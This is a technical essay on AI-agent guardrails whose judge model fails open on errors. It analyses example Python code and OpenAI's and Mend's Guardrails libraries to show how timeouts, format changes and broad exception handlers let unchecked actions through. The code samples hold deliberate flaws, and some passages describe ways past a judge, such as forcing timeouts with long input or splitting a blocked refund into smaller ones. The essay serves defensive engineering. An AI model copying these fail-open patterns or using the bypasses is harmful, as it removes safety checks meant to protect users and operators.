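# Judge-model guardrails that raise on a policy block and ignore their own errors

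## How the pattern works and why programmers write it

An AI agent is a program in which a language model chooses actions and ordinary software carries them out. For example, the model might read a customer's complaint, look up the order and ask the software to issue a refund. The model can choose badly, and strangers can plant instructions in the text it reads, so developers often add a guardrail, which is a check that can stop content or an agent's action before it takes effect. Some guardrails are plain rules, such as a list of forbidden commands. Others ask a second language model, the judge, whether to allow or block the proposed action. The judge returns its decision, called the verdict, in a form the program can read.

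A policy block occurs when the judge returns a verdict of block and the guardrail stops the agent. A judge error is any failure that leaves the guardrail without a verdict. The judge, which usually runs on another machine, may take too long, its provider may refuse the request, its answer may be unreadable, or the guardrail's own code may have a bug. The programmer has to decide what happens to the action after a judge error, and one common way of writing the check lets the action proceed as if the judge had approved it.

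Judge errors are a normal part of running such a check. tianpan.co's *Your Guardrail Is a Model Too*, a blog post on guardrails in production, gives 15 to 40 milliseconds per check for a small detector of jailbreaks (attempts to talk a model out of its rules) and under 90 milliseconds for a dedicated moderation classifier. A judge with eight billion parameters is a full language model, with slow starts, queues and occasional very late answers. Teams also tend to give the guardrail much less computing capacity than the main model, so it is the first to become overloaded when traffic rises. Timeouts are therefore likely to cluster at the busiest hours.

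### Twelve lines of Python

Programs report problems through exceptions. A program normally runs its instructions in order, and a function (a named group of instructions) that calls another waits for the result before continuing. An exception interrupts this order. It passes from the function where it arises to the caller, then to the caller's caller, until one of them handles it. If none does, the program usually stops. In Python, the language of the example below, `raise` triggers an exception, and `except` begins a handler, a group of instructions that runs when an exception of the named kind arrives. The line numbers on the left are only for reference.

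```python
 1  def check(action):
 2      try:
 3          reply = ask_judge(action, timeout=5)
 4          verdict = json.loads(reply)["verdict"]
 5          if verdict == "block":
 6              raise PolicyBlock(action)
 7          return "allow"
 8      except PolicyBlock:
 9          raise
10      except Exception as error:
11          log.warning("judge failed: %s", error)
12          return "allow"
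```

Line 1 names the function, `check`, and its input, the action the agent wants to take. The agent's software calls `check` before it carries out any action, and goes ahead only if `check` returns "allow" rather than raising an exception. Line 2 starts the block of code covered by the exception handlers further down.

Line 3 sends the action to the judge and waits at most five seconds, after which `ask_judge` raises a timeout exception. The judge replies in JSON, a text format for named fields, and the reply might read `{"verdict": "block"}`. On line 4, `json.loads` turns that text into something the program can search, and the rest of the line picks out the "verdict" field. Line 5 compares the field with the word "block". If they match, line 6 raises PolicyBlock, an exception the programmer defined for this purpose. Otherwise, line 7 returns "allow".

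The handlers start at line 8, which catches a PolicyBlock. Line 9, a bare `raise`, re-raises it, meaning that it sends the exception on unchanged to the caller. Line 10 catches `Exception`, a category that includes almost every ordinary Python error. Line 11 writes a warning to the log, the record engineers check when something goes wrong, and line 12 returns "allow". Programmers say that lines 10 to 12 swallow the exception, because they catch it, log it and let the program continue.

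Lines 8 and 9 catch PolicyBlock and re-raise it so that the handler in line 10 doesn't catch it. Python tries handlers from top to bottom and uses the first that matches, and PolicyBlock, like most custom exceptions, is a subclass of `Exception`. Without lines 8 and 9, a block verdict would produce a log entry reading "judge failed", followed by "allow", and the guardrail could never stop anything.

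A programmer who forgets the first handler will probably find out soon, because the most obvious test of a guardrail is to give it forbidden input. Adding lines 8 and 9 makes that test pass, and a test with harmless input passes too. The guardrail now behaves correctly whenever the judge gives a readable verdict, but neither test covers what happens when the judge doesn't give one.

### Five inputs, one of them permanent

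The table shows how the code handles five replies. In the second, fourth and fifth rows, the judge had decided, or was partway through writing, that the action should not go ahead.

| What comes back from the judge | Path through the code | Result for the caller | The action |
|---|---|---|---|
| `{"verdict": "allow"}` | Line 5 finds no match; line 7 returns | "allow" | Runs, with approval |
| `{"verdict": "block"}` | Line 6 raises PolicyBlock; lines 8 and 9 re-raise it | PolicyBlock | Stops |
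| Nothing within five seconds | Line 3 raises a timeout; lines 10 to 12 swallow it | "allow" | Runs without a verdict |
| `{"verdict": "blo` (malformed JSON, cut off in mid-word) | Line 4 fails to read the text; lines 10 to 12 swallow the error | "allow" | Runs without a verdict |
| `{"decision": "block"}` (the output format has changed) | Line 4 finds no field named "verdict" and raises a KeyError; lines 10 to 12 swallow it | "allow" | Runs against the judge's decision |

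The caller gets the same word in four of the five rows, so it cannot distinguish an action that the judge approved from one that the judge never received. No code further up can recover that distinction, because the information is gone by the time `check` returns.

The failure in the last row lasts longer than the two above it. A timeout affects one request, and the next may well succeed. A KeyError (Python's exception for a missing field) after a format change recurs on every request, because every reply now lacks the field. Suppose a company's agents make 2,000 checks a day and one check in 200 times out. Ten actions a day then go ahead without a verdict. If someone renames the field on a Friday evening, all 2,000 actions a day go ahead without one, and by Monday morning the total is around 5,000. Providers of hosted moderation services ship new versions on their own schedule, as tianpan.co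 points out, so the change can come from outside the company. An engineer who rewords the judge's instructions can also cause the same failure without touching the code.

This is easy to miss. No user sees an error, and the agents finish their tasks, perhaps a little more smoothly than before. The log fills up, but the entries resemble those the engineers already know from the daily timeouts. The new entries are also cryptic. Line 11 would print `judge failed: 'verdict'`, because the text of a KeyError is just the name of the missing field. The drop to zero blocks is hard to notice at first, because if the judge normally blocks two actions a day on average, at random, a day without any block occurs about once a week anyway. Every item goes through until someone reads the log closely or counts the failures.

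A related failure does not even leave a log entry. Suppose the field keeps its name but the judge starts to write "deny" instead of "block". Line 5 finds no match, line 7 returns "allow", and no exception is raised. The fault is in line 5 rather than the handlers, because line 5 checks only for "block" and treats every other value as permission.

### Fail open, fail closed and a principle from 1975

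When a check has no verdict, it fails open if it lets the content or action through and fails closed if it stops it. The example fails open. If line 12 were `raise` instead of `return "allow"`, it would fail closed, because the timeout or KeyError would reach the caller and halt the action. A post on tianpan.co describes code that catches an error, logs it and continues as a typical case of failing open. It adds that almost no team could name its own guardrail's default, because the default usually results from the exception handling rather than a deliberate choice. The post cites no survey, so "almost no team" is at best an experienced guess, but the explanation is plausible because line 12 looks like tidying up and a reviewer could easily overlook it.

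Computer security had a preference between the two long before language models existed. In *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975), Saltzer and Schroeder set out eight design principles for systems that control who may use stored information. One of them, which they credit to a suggestion by E. Glaser in 1965, is fail-safe defaults: "Base access decisions on permission rather than exclusion." Nobody has access by default, and the system identifies the conditions that permit it. They thought it was wrong to look for reasons to refuse access instead, because the designers of a large system will not have thought properly about every object.

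Their main argument is that mistakes are easier to notice in a mechanism that works by granting permission. A mistake there tends to make it refuse access, and people who cannot get at their files complain quickly. In a mechanism that works by exclusion, a mistake tends to allow access, and nobody may notice in normal use. The second case fits both the KeyError above and the judge that starts to write "deny". The example breaks the principle in lines 5 and 12, and a repair has to deal with both. Saltzer and Schroeder also ask that a system check every access to every object, including during recovery and maintenance. An agent whose guardrail fails open does not meet that requirement when the guardrail fails.

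The principle may not fully carry over to judge models. The 1975 paper had in view a computer comparing a user's name with a list, which seldom fails to give an answer, whereas a judge called over a network fails routinely. Refusals may also be less conspicuous than the paper assumed. In a passage on false alarms, tianpan.co observes that users whom a guardrail wrongly blocks rarely report it; they rephrase, try again or leave. So a guardrail that fails closed on one request in 200 might also go unnoticed for some time. The 1975 argument is strongest when the failure is permanent, because a guardrail that fails closed on every request would soon be noticed. The paper offers its principles as warnings that a design needs a careful look, not as absolute rules.

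### Where today's catalogues place it

The US non-profit MITRE maintains the Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE), a numbered catalogue of the kinds of flaw that make software vulnerable. *CWE-636*, "Not Failing Securely", also known as "Failing Open", covers products that by design respond to an error by falling back to a less secure state than others available, such as the most permissive access rules. Line 12 closely fits this definition. MITRE lists the consequences as the bypass of a protection mechanism, often contrary to what the administrator expects, and at the least a false sense of security.

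The same entry gives an example from network hardware. A switch uses a table to send each piece of traffic only to the machine that should receive it. When that table overflows, some switches send everything to every machine, so an eavesdropper can flood the table with false entries and then read other people's traffic. An attacker could similarly send a judge text that reliably causes an error, such as a document long enough to push the judge past its five-second limit. The code above ignores judge errors, so the text would get through without the judge's approval.

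MITRE links CWE-636 to both the 1975 paper and the "Top Ten", a list of the most critical risks to web applications maintained by OWASP, a foundation that publishes guidance on software security. The current edition, from 2025, has a new category, A10:2025, "Mishandling of Exceptional Conditions". Secure Code Warrior's *New Risk Category on the OWASP Top Ten* (2025), from a company that trains developers, repeats OWASP's explanation that an application may fail to prevent an unusual condition, fail to detect it, or respond to it badly. The example code detects the condition on line 11 but responds to it badly. eSecurity Planet's *OWASP Top 10 2025 Released* (2025), a trade-press report, recommends systems that fail closed, so that security controls stay in force under abnormal conditions.

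The category is a wide one. MITRE's *OWASP Top Ten 2025 Category A10:2025* lists 24 weaknesses in it, down to division by zero, and describes such categories as informal groupings, unsuitable for classifying an actual vulnerability. Three of the 24 bear directly on the example:

- CWE-396, a handler for generic exceptions, is line 10.
- CWE-390, detecting an error without acting on it, describes line 11, unless one counts a log entry as action.
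- CWE-636 itself is line 12.

None of these entries is about AI, and none needs to be, since the fault sits in the ordinary code around the judge.

How often the pattern occurs in practice is harder to establish. When MITRE catalogued the weakness in 2008, it noted that few public examples existed, because design flaws are hard to fix and people rarely report them. By the end of August 2026, GCVE's *Not Failing Securely ('Failing Open')*, a page in a public vulnerability database, listed 129 examples. One concerns OpenClaw, an AI agent program. Its handler for messages from the chat service Mattermost could "fall open" when the channel type was missing. The advisory has since been withdrawn as a duplicate. The entry does not involve a judge, but a missing field that leads to permission is much the same failure as the KeyError in the table. The count of 129 is weak evidence of how common the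 failure is in guardrails, because public databases mostly hold flaws in products that other people install, and a company's private twelve-line guardrail is unlikely to appear in one.

### The case for carrying on

The programmer who writes line 12 usually wants, reasonably, to keep a broken check from taking the product down. An unhandled exception usually ends a Python program. O'Reilly's *Failure to Handle Errors Correctly*, a chapter of the book *24 Deadly Sins of Software Security*, notes that any such crash denies people the service and can therefore be a security problem, especially on a server. Saltzer and Schroeder's view partly supports this, since they counted it as a security violation, alongside theft and tampering, when an intruder keeps authorised users from their information. A general handler around code that calls an unreliable service is thus normal defensive practice,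 and few programmers would object to line 10 on its own.

The concern is greater for agents, because one task may involve many checks. If the 2,000 daily checks at the company from before come from 40 tasks with 50 checked actions each, and one check in 200 fails independently of the others, a task has a 0.995^50, or about 78%, chance of finishing without a failed check. With a guardrail that fails closed and doesn't retry, about 22% of tasks would stop partway through for reasons unrelated to the agent's actions. Few teams would tolerate that for long, and in some real outages failing closed has stopped a whole product. With a guardrail that fails open, those tasks would continue, but each would include at least one action that no judge approved.

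Lecture slides on defensive programming from James Madison University list a "neutral value" among the things a function can return after an error, and warn of a possible trade-off between correctness and robustness. Many functions have a neutral value. For example, a program that cannot load a user's photograph can harmlessly show a grey outline. A guardrail can only allow or block, and neither is neutral. "Allow" seems neutral because the program then runs as it would without a guardrail, which is presumably why it appears in line 12. MITRE describes the motive as a wish to "fail functional" in order to save on administration and support.

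Whether that wish is reasonable depends on what the guardrail protects. According to tianpan.co, failing open for ten minutes may be acceptable, even correct, for a coding assistant whose filter mostly catches passwords left in the output by accident, but unacceptable for a chat product with children among its users or a filter that enforces a legal boundary in healthcare. That seems right for a short outage, but the KeyError is a bug and will not go away by itself. The need for availability justifies letting some actions through while the judge is briefly unreachable. Because line 10 catches `Exception`, it treats a bug the same way as a slow network and keeps letting actions through even when the guardrail has stopped working for good.

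## OpenAI's Guardrails library, where execution errors pass by default

OpenAI publishes Guardrails, a free Python and TypeScript library of checks for applications that use language models. Like the twelve-line example, it stops a request when a check finds a violation. If the check itself hits an error, the request continues unless the developer has changed a setting.

A program usually reaches a language model through a client, a piece of software that sends the request and hands back the answer. The library provides clients that take the place of OpenAI's ordinary ones. In OpenAI's *Quickstart*, the developer replaces `AsyncOpenAI` with `GuardrailsAsyncOpenAI` and gives it a configuration file that lists the checks. The rest of the program needs almost no changes. The checks run in up to three stages:

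- Preflight checks run before the model receives the message, for example to mask personal data.
- Input checks, such as jailbreak detection, run in parallel with the model call.
- Output checks examine the text that the model generates.

Some of these checks use a judge. The TypeScript edition of OpenAI's *Quickstart* lists jailbreak detection and custom prompt checks as using a language model, and the personal-data, moderation and URL checks as not using one. The moderation check can still time out, because it calls OpenAI's moderation service over the network. For agents, the library has `GuardrailAgent`, which looks for planted instructions before and after each tool call (the model's request for the software to do something).

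### Two paths through the code

Each check returns a result object with a `tripwire_triggered` field, which shows whether the guardrail found a violation. OpenAI calls this flag a tripwire. If it is True, the library raises a GuardrailTripwireTriggered exception, and the application doesn't receive the model's answer. OpenAI's *Tripwires* says developers who would rather handle violations themselves can set `suppress_tripwire=True`. The client then raises no exception and returns the answer together with the results, which the application has to check for violations.

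OpenAI uses the term "execution failure" for a check that breaks down while running. The term covers both judge errors and faults in checks that have no judge. The code below is simplified from the source code in OpenAI's *Runtime*.

```python
 1  try:
 2      result = await guardrail.run(context, text)
 3  except Exception as error:
 4      log.error("guardrail failed: %s", error)
 5      if raise_guardrail_errors:
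 6          raise
 7      result = GuardrailResult(tripwire_triggered=False,
 8                               execution_failed=True,
 9                               original_exception=error)
10
11  # after all the checks have finished
12  if result.tripwire_triggered:
13      raise GuardrailTripwireTriggered(result)
```

Line 2 runs the check, and line 3 catches almost any error it raises. Line 5 reads the setting `raise_guardrail_errors`, which is False unless the developer changes it, so lines 7 to 9 normally create a substitute result with the tripwire off. Line 12 then finds no violation, and the request continues. Line 13 raises the exception for a policy block outside the `try` block, so the handler on line 3 cannot catch it and the library doesn't need a separate handler to re-raise it.

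The same handler can discard a violation that a check has already found. OpenAI's *Types* requires every result to include the examined text in a field named `checked_text`, and Python raises an error if a check creates a result without it. If a custom check detects a violation but its developer forgot this field, the error reaches line 3, and the library replaces the violation with a result whose tripwire is off. A first test with forbidden input would probably reveal the mistake.

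### One mistyped model name

OpenAI gives an invalid model name as its example of an execution failure. Suppose a company runs a customer-service assistant with two input checks, moderation and jailbreak detection. The developer wants `gpt-4.1-mini` as the jailbreak judge but types `gpt-4.1-mni`.

When the application starts, the library validates the configuration file and raises an exception if a check's settings have the wrong form. The mistyped model name passes because it is still text. When the first customer writes, the library requests a model that doesn't exist, the provider rejects the request, and the check ends in an error. The library then creates its substitute result with the tripwire off, and the main model, whose name is spelled correctly, answers as usual. As with the renamed field in the twelve-line example, the same thing happens with every later message, so none is checked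 for jailbreaks until someone corrects the name.

The client still appears to have its guardrails. The program uses `GuardrailsAsyncOpenAI`, the configuration file lists jailbreak detection, and the moderation check works, so a hateful test message triggers a tripwire. To find the fault, someone would have to read the log or test an actual jailbreak. The jailbreak test could still miss the fault, because the main model might refuse on its own and the tester could credit the guardrail.

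A typing mistake is present at launch, so someone could find it then. But the provider could also withdraw the judge model months later, and the check would then fail in the same way even though nobody had changed the configuration.

One sign of the errors is the number of tokens (the units of text by which providers charge) that the judges have used, which a function in the TypeScript library adds up. In this example the total should drop to zero, because the moderation check uses none, but this helps only if someone is monitoring the total.

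### What the library records about a failure

The twelve-line example returned "allow" for both approval and failure, so the application could not tell them apart. OpenAI's library records the difference. When a check fails to execute, its result contains `execution_failed=True`, the original exception, the guardrail's name, the stage and the error message. The application can read the results in `response.guardrail_results` or supply a function that the library calls after each check. With a few lines of code, a developer who knows about the `execution_failed` field can count failures or withhold the answer after one.

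The quickstart doesn't mention the field, however. It says only that the system continues and returns `tripwire_triggered=False`. OpenAI's sample code for `suppress_tripwire` checks only `tripwire_triggered` in the results, so an application that copies it treats a check that hit an error like one that found nothing. Some developers can't easily access the results at all. OpenAI mentions, in a note on token counting, that the JavaScript version of its Agents SDK, a toolkit for building agents, doesn't include guardrail results in the result of a run.

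The default did not change between late 2025 and February 2026. The earlier edition of OpenAI's *Quickstart* has the same two error modes, default and example of the invalid model name. The result object already had the fields that record a failure in October 2025. OpenAI still labelled the Python package a preview in March 2026, at version 0.2.1, although the overview in OpenAI's *Guardrails* calls the library "production ready".

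### What strict mode asks of the application

Setting `raise_guardrail_errors=True` makes the library fail closed, because an execution failure then raises an exception and the application gets no answer to pass on. OpenAI's sample programs catch only `GuardrailTripwireTriggered`. With this setting, a timeout in the judge would get past that handler and, unless something further up caught it, end the program or at least the request, so the customer would see a crash.

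These failures are also hard to handle precisely. The Python edition of OpenAI's *Exceptions* has a class for violations and one for faulty configuration, but none for execution failures, so the application receives whatever error the check ran into, such as a KeyError, a timeout or a refusal from the provider. The call to the main model can also time out or be refused, and the application can't tell from the exception's type which call failed. Suppose it responds to a timeout by sending the message to a backup model through an ordinary client. That is sensible if the main model timed out, but if the judge did, the message reaches a model without any guardrail. The TypeScript edition of *Exceptions* defines a separate GuardrailExecutionError, which would let an application tell the two apart.

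In Python, the library runs its checks together in a task group. When one check raises an exception, Python cancels the others and wraps the exception in an `ExceptionGroup`. An ordinary timeout handler does not catch a group that contains a timeout, so unless another part of the client unwraps the group, the developer needs a general handler or `except*`. If a check instead catches its own error and returns a result marked as failed, the library waits for all the checks to finish and raises the original exception without a wrapper. The application should therefore handle both forms.

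When a check returns its failure in this way, the library looks for failures before it looks for tripwires. If the jailbreak judge fails while the moderation check finds a violation, the library reports only the failure to the application. This makes no difference if the application stops in both cases. But if the application catches the failure and continues, on the assumption that an outage is harmless, it also continues despite the violation.

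### Mend's version of the same library

Mend, a software-security company, publishes a Python library that presumably derives from OpenAI's. The error-handling code in Mend's *Runtime* matches OpenAI's almost line for line, including the comments, and OpenAI's licence permits copying. In both libraries, a check that fails with an error does not stop the request by default.

Mend's *Error handling* documentation lists typical causes of execution errors, including a bad configuration, a missing software component, an invalid model name and a network error inside the check. A failed check produces a result with `execution_failed=True`, and the documentation recommends inspecting results for this field if an application needs to react to failures. OpenAI's library sets the same field, but its quickstart doesn't mention it.

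The field distinguishes a check that found nothing from one that never finished, so an application can use it to count failures and raise an alarm, but the field doesn't block anything by itself. The application sees it when the client returns the model's answer. At that point the application can still withhold the answer, but if a preflight check that masks personal data has failed, for example, the message has presumably already gone to the model unmasked. Existing programs that read only the violation field will behave as before.

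Mend's library also differs from OpenAI's in that even a genuine violation raises no exception unless the developer sets `suppress_enforcement=False` (Mend, *Enforcement*). The table shows how the settings combine.

| Library and settings | After a violation | After an execution failure |
|---|---|---|
| OpenAI, defaults | Exception | Request continues |
| OpenAI, `suppress_tripwire=True` | Request continues | Request continues |
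| OpenAI, `raise_guardrail_errors=True` | Exception | Exception |
| Mend, defaults | Request continues | Request continues |
| Mend, `suppress_enforcement=False` | Exception | Request continues |
| Mend, `suppress_enforcement=False` and `raise_guardrail_errors=True` | Exception | Exception |

By default, Mend's library only monitors. It reports both violations and failures and leaves the response to the application. It can also send each result to an audit server, where a team could count the failures. The risk comes when a developer switches on enforcement, because the guardrail then blocks forbidden input in every test and the developer may not realise that a second setting governs errors. If that setting is left unchanged, the application blocks violations but lets execution errors pass, as it would under the defaults in OpenAI's library.

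### Two meanings of "fail-safe"

OpenAI calls the permissive default "Fail-Safe Mode" and the strict alternative "Fail-Secure Mode", and Mend uses the same terms. In the older security usage of Saltzer and Schroeder, a fail-safe default denies access. Guardrails in fail-safe mode let through messages they have failed to check, but an auditor who knows the older usage could reasonably conclude that they block them.

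OpenAI's usage has a precedent in door locks. A fail-safe lock opens when the power fails, so that people can get out of a burning building, and a fail-secure lock stays shut. But opening the door protects the people inside, whereas a guardrail that opens mainly keeps the service available and leaves whoever the check was meant to protect exposed. The terms "fail open" and "fail closed" avoid this confusion, and Mend describes its strict mode as a way to "fail closed".

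In the source code, OpenAI also describes the default as treating execution errors "as safe", even though no check has finished examining the text.

Neither the quickstart nor the source code gives a reason for the default. A comment next to the substitute result says that execution errors should not trigger the tripwire, but not why the request should continue. Mend comes closer by noting that an execution error does not count as a safety violation. That is a good reason to keep the two fields apart, because a broken check is no evidence that the customer did anything wrong, and mixing the two in a log would inflate the violation count. But it doesn't justify letting the request through, because the library could record an error as an error and still stop the request, as it does in strict mode.

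OpenAI more likely chose this default because it promises a drop-in replacement. Developers who swap one client for another expect the application to run as before, and a strict default would add a new way for every request to fail. Some would probably respond to the extra errors by removing the guardrail.

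## How a deliberate block can itself be lost

Lines 8 and 9 of the twelve-line example pass a PolicyBlock to the caller of `check`. The agent stops only if the code further up lets the exception through, recognises it, and receives it before the action has run. A large agent program can have many layers between the guardrail and the code that stops the agent, often written by different people, and any of them can lose the block.

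### Exceptions that broad handlers should miss

Some of Python's own exceptions are requests to stop rather than errors. Pressing Control-C raises KeyboardInterrupt, and a program that calls `sys.exit()` to end itself raises SystemExit. A programmer who writes `except Exception` to survive ordinary errors rarely wants to catch either of them. Python's designers therefore placed both outside `Exception`, as this simplified family tree shows:

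```
BaseException
 ├── KeyboardInterrupt
 ├── SystemExit
 ├── asyncio.CancelledError   (since Python 3.8)
 └── Exception
      ├── KeyError, TimeoutError and other ordinary errors
      └── PolicyBlock
```

A handler catches the class it names and all its subclasses, so `except Exception` catches a PolicyBlock but not a KeyboardInterrupt. According to Python's official *Built-in Exceptions* documentation, KeyboardInterrupt is left out so that code catching `Exception` doesn't accidentally keep a program from exiting.

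Until 2019, CancelledError was a subclass of `Exception`. Python's asyncio, which lets one program switch between many tasks while they wait for networks or files, raises CancelledError inside a task when the program cancels it. Коренберг (2018) reported on Python's issue tracker that code which caught `Exception`, logged it and tried again later was also swallowing cancellations, so some tasks could not be cancelled. The workaround was to place `except CancelledError: raise` above `except Exception`, the same structure as lines 8 to 12 of the example.

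Guido van Rossum, Python's creator, at first thought moving the exception was too risky and blamed the broad handlers instead. Andrew Svetlov, another Python developer, found that even experienced people constantly forgot the extra clause. Yury Selivanov closed the proposal in May 2018 but reopened it in September, after at least eight people at conferences that summer told him about cancellation bugs that were very hard to trace. When he made the change, Selivanov (2019) described it in *bpo-32528* as a remedy for a common mistake.

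The change affects judges because applications often set a deadline for a whole request and cancel whatever is still running when it expires. Before Python 3.8, if an asyncio version of `check` was cancelled while waiting for its judge, line 10 caught the cancellation and the function returned "allow". Since 3.8, line 10 does not catch the cancellation, so it propagates to the caller.

### Moving PolicyBlock outside Exception

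A programmer could give policy blocks the same protection by writing `class PolicyBlock(BaseException)`. Lines 8 and 9 would then be unnecessary, because line 10 could no longer catch the block. No other `except Exception` between the guardrail and the top of the program could catch it either.

Python's documentation advises against this and recommends deriving custom exceptions from `Exception`. One practical reason is that some broad handlers do necessary work. In the discussion that Коренберг started, Bruce Merry described code that caught `Exception`, undid any half-finished operations and then re-raised. After the upgrade to Python 3.8, cancellations skipped that handler, so those operations were no longer undone. An agent that reserves stock before it places an order could have the same problem, since a policy block would bypass the handler that releases the stock. Clean-up code in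 a `finally` clause would still run. Merry still welcomed the change, because while checking his handlers he found places where it had fixed hidden bugs.

Other software may also be unprepared for an exception outside `Exception`. A web server typically catches `Exception` around each request and returns an error page. A PolicyBlock outside `Exception` would get past that handler and might end a process that was also serving other customers. In a message quoted by Selivanov (2018) in *Why not using "except: (...) raise" to cleanup on error?*, van Rossum considered it a flaw that asyncio's code generally caught only `Exception`. Selivanov had to improve how asyncio handled these exceptions before he could move CancelledError outside `Exception`.

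Deriving the block exception from `BaseException` doesn't fully protect it, because a bare `except:` or an `except BaseException` still catches it. The approach is probably worth considering for a single team that can read through all its own handlers. It is harder to justify in a published library, whose users expect `except Exception` to catch whatever the library raises and might not learn that it misses a block until one takes down their server.

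### A handler further up

Many agent programs run a series of plug-ins before each action. One might record the action, another might add up costs, and a third might be the guardrail. To keep a faulty plug-in from crashing the agent, the programmer catches their errors:

```python
for plugin in plugins:
    try:
        plugin(action)
    except Exception as error:
        log.warning("plugin failed: %s", error)
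run_tool(action)
```

If `check` is one of the plug-ins, this handler catches its PolicyBlock, and `run_tool` carries out the action that the judge just blocked. A test of `check` on its own would still pass, because `check` does raise the exception. To find the fault, a test has to run the whole loop with a forbidden action and verify whether the action took place.

The same could happen with OpenAI's Agents SDK. Its exception for a blocked tool call derives from `AgentsException`, which is a subclass of `Exception`, so a developer who wraps the whole run in a broad handler will catch violations along with network errors.

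### A retry library that wraps the exception

Calls to a judge fail often enough that programmers like to retry them. A typical retry helper tries three times and then raises an exception of its own:

```python
def with_retries(function, action):
    for attempt in range(3):
        try:
            return function(action)
        except Exception as error:
            last_error = error
    raise RetryError("gave up") from last_error

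try:
    with_retries(check, action)
except PolicyBlock:
    stop_agent()
except RetryError:
    log.warning("judge unavailable, continuing")
run_tool(action)
```

Suppose the judge blocks the action all three times. The helper catches each PolicyBlock as if it were a network fault and finally raises a RetryError. Python stores the original exception in the new one's `__cause__` attribute and prints both in a full traceback. But `except PolicyBlock` checks only the class of the new exception, RetryError, so it doesn't match. The last handler therefore logs an outage that never happened, and the action runs.

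The retries can also overturn a block before any wrapping happens. If a judge blocks a borderline action nine times out of ten, and its answers are independent, the chance of three blocks in a row is 0.9³, or about 73%. In the other 27% of cases, one of the attempts returns "allow", and the helper passes that on as the result. If the helper were wrapped around the twelve-line example, it would retry almost only PolicyBlock exceptions, because `check` catches and ignores its own judge errors.

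A helper that retries only timeouts and refused connections would avoid both problems, because a PolicyBlock would leave it at once and unchanged.

A block can also be lost when a company's guardrail package and its agent program each define their own PolicyBlock class. Despite the shared name, a handler for one class misses exceptions of the other, unless the second class derives from the first. A similar confusion broke one programmer's code in Python 3.8, when CancelledError moved. The code caught `concurrent.futures.CancelledError`, as at least two Stack Overflow answers had suggested, rather than `asyncio.CancelledError`.

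### A task group that delivers a package

A team with two checks can save time by running them concurrently in a task group. Python then wraps even a single exception in an ExceptionGroup, as happens in OpenAI's Guardrails library, because more than one task can fail.

```python
try:
    async with asyncio.TaskGroup() as group:
        group.create_task(check_content(action))
        group.create_task(check_budget(action))
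except PolicyBlock:
    stop_agent()
except Exception as error:
    log.warning("checks failed: %s", error)
await run_tool(action)
```

If `check_content` raises a PolicyBlock, the TaskGroup wraps it in an ExceptionGroup, so the handler for PolicyBlock doesn't match. ExceptionGroup is a subclass of `Exception`, so the last handler catches it and the agent runs the tool. The log entry is "checks failed: unhandled errors in a TaskGroup (1 sub-exception)", with no mention of a policy.

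Python 3.11 introduced exception groups and a handler for them, `except*`, which matches the exceptions inside a group. `except* PolicyBlock` would catch the block. It would also catch a PolicyBlock raised outside a group, so the same handler works for checks that run one after another. Python doesn't allow `except` and `except*` in the same `try` statement, so the programmer has to convert all the handlers in that statement at once.

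Deriving `PolicyBlock` from `BaseException` would help here too. A group with at least one member from outside `Exception` is a `BaseExceptionGroup`, which `except Exception` doesn't catch. The block would then get past the last handler above, so the tool would not run, but neither would `stop_agent`.

With `return_exceptions=True`, `asyncio.gather`, an older way to run tasks together, puts each task's exception in the list of results instead of raising it. A PolicyBlock then has no effect unless the program checks the results for it.

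### A tool wrapper that turns the block into text

Tools fail often, and a model can usually recover if it learns what went wrong. Agent frameworks therefore tend to turn a tool's exceptions into text for the model:

```python
def call_tool(tool, arguments):
    try:
        return tool(arguments)
    except Exception as error:
        return f"Error: {error}"
```

Suppose the tool issues refunds and calls `check` before it pays out. The judge blocks a refund of £900, the wrapper returns "Error: refund of £900", and the model treats the message much like one about a mistyped order number. The £900 has not been paid, but the agent is still running and may try another way to finish its task, such as issuing three refunds of £300. A judge that sees each one separately may allow them.

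Whether this counts as losing the block depends on the block's purpose. A message to the model is a sensible response if the policy only forbids that one refund, but the agent should stop altogether if the request suggests that a stranger has taken control of it. OpenAI's Agents SDK offers both responses in its tool guardrails, which check individual tool calls. In the JavaScript version, `rejectContent` skips the call and sends the model a message, while `throwException` raises an error to end the run.

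A developer who raises an exception to stop the agent may still end up with only a message. In *OpenAI Agents agent guard*, a guide to using its product with the Agents SDK, the security company Arcjet warns developers not to raise exceptions from a tool guardrail, because the exception either halts the run or disappears into the SDK's default function for tool errors. Arcjet's own integration always rejects with a message, which makes the outcome predictable but gives up the option of stopping the agent.

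According to OpenAI's *Release process/changelog*, since version 0.8.0 of the Python SDK, the default when a local MCP tool fails can be to send the model an error message instead of failing the whole run. MCP, the Model Context Protocol, is a standard for linking models to outside software. A company that relied on an exception from these tools to end the run could lose that protection by upgrading. It can restore the old behaviour by setting `failure_error_function` to `None`, but it has to do so separately for every server that has its own error handler.

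Once an exception has become text, a program can no longer reliably identify it. GitLab's *Tool error propagation differs on a per tool basis* describes agent code in which one function turns an exception that escapes a tool into a set phrase such as "execution failed due to", and another searches the tool's replies for these phrases to determine whether the tool failed. Many tools catch their own exceptions, so the first function never adds its phrase. A PolicyBlock caught inside such a tool would presumably look like a successful call.

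Pydantic AI, another Python framework for agents, took the stricter approach. In *More flexible tool exception handling*, strawgate objected that any tool exception ended the run unless it was a specific request for the model to retry, so users often had to rewrite their functions. strawgate proposed catching tool exceptions by default and turning them into retry requests. That would make ordinary errors less disruptive, but it would also turn a policy block into a retry request unless the framework exempted it.

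### A block that arrives after the action

A block can reach the right handler in the right form and still arrive too late to stop a tool call. By default, the Agents SDK starts an input guardrail, which checks the user's message, at the same time as the agent. If the judge takes 900 milliseconds, the model calls a tool after 600, and the tool runs for another 100, the tool finishes 200 milliseconds before the block arrives.

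The problem came up soon after the SDK's release. In March 2025, *Wait to run the Agent first step until Input guardrails is complete* (rach, 2025) proposed that the agent should wait for the guardrail, and gave the example of a guardrail against deleting files on an agent with access to a file system. An OpenAI maintainer closed the proposal three days later because the behaviour was intended and documented, and suggested that developers who wanted to wait could run the check in their own code first. The maintainer later gave latency as the reason for the behaviour, since the agent has already made progress if the guardrail finds nothing wrong.

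In a later GitHub bug report about version 0.1.0, *Input guardrail tripwire allows tool execution to continue after exception is raised* (issue 991, by adeelmc), the guardrail raised its exception correctly, but OpenAI's trace, a record of what the agent did, showed tools running afterwards. The maintainer had defended a design in which a tool can finish before the verdict because the guardrail runs in parallel with the agent. The evidence in the report is a single trace, without the code that produced it, but it describes a worse problem, in which the agent keeps starting tools after the guardrail has blocked it.

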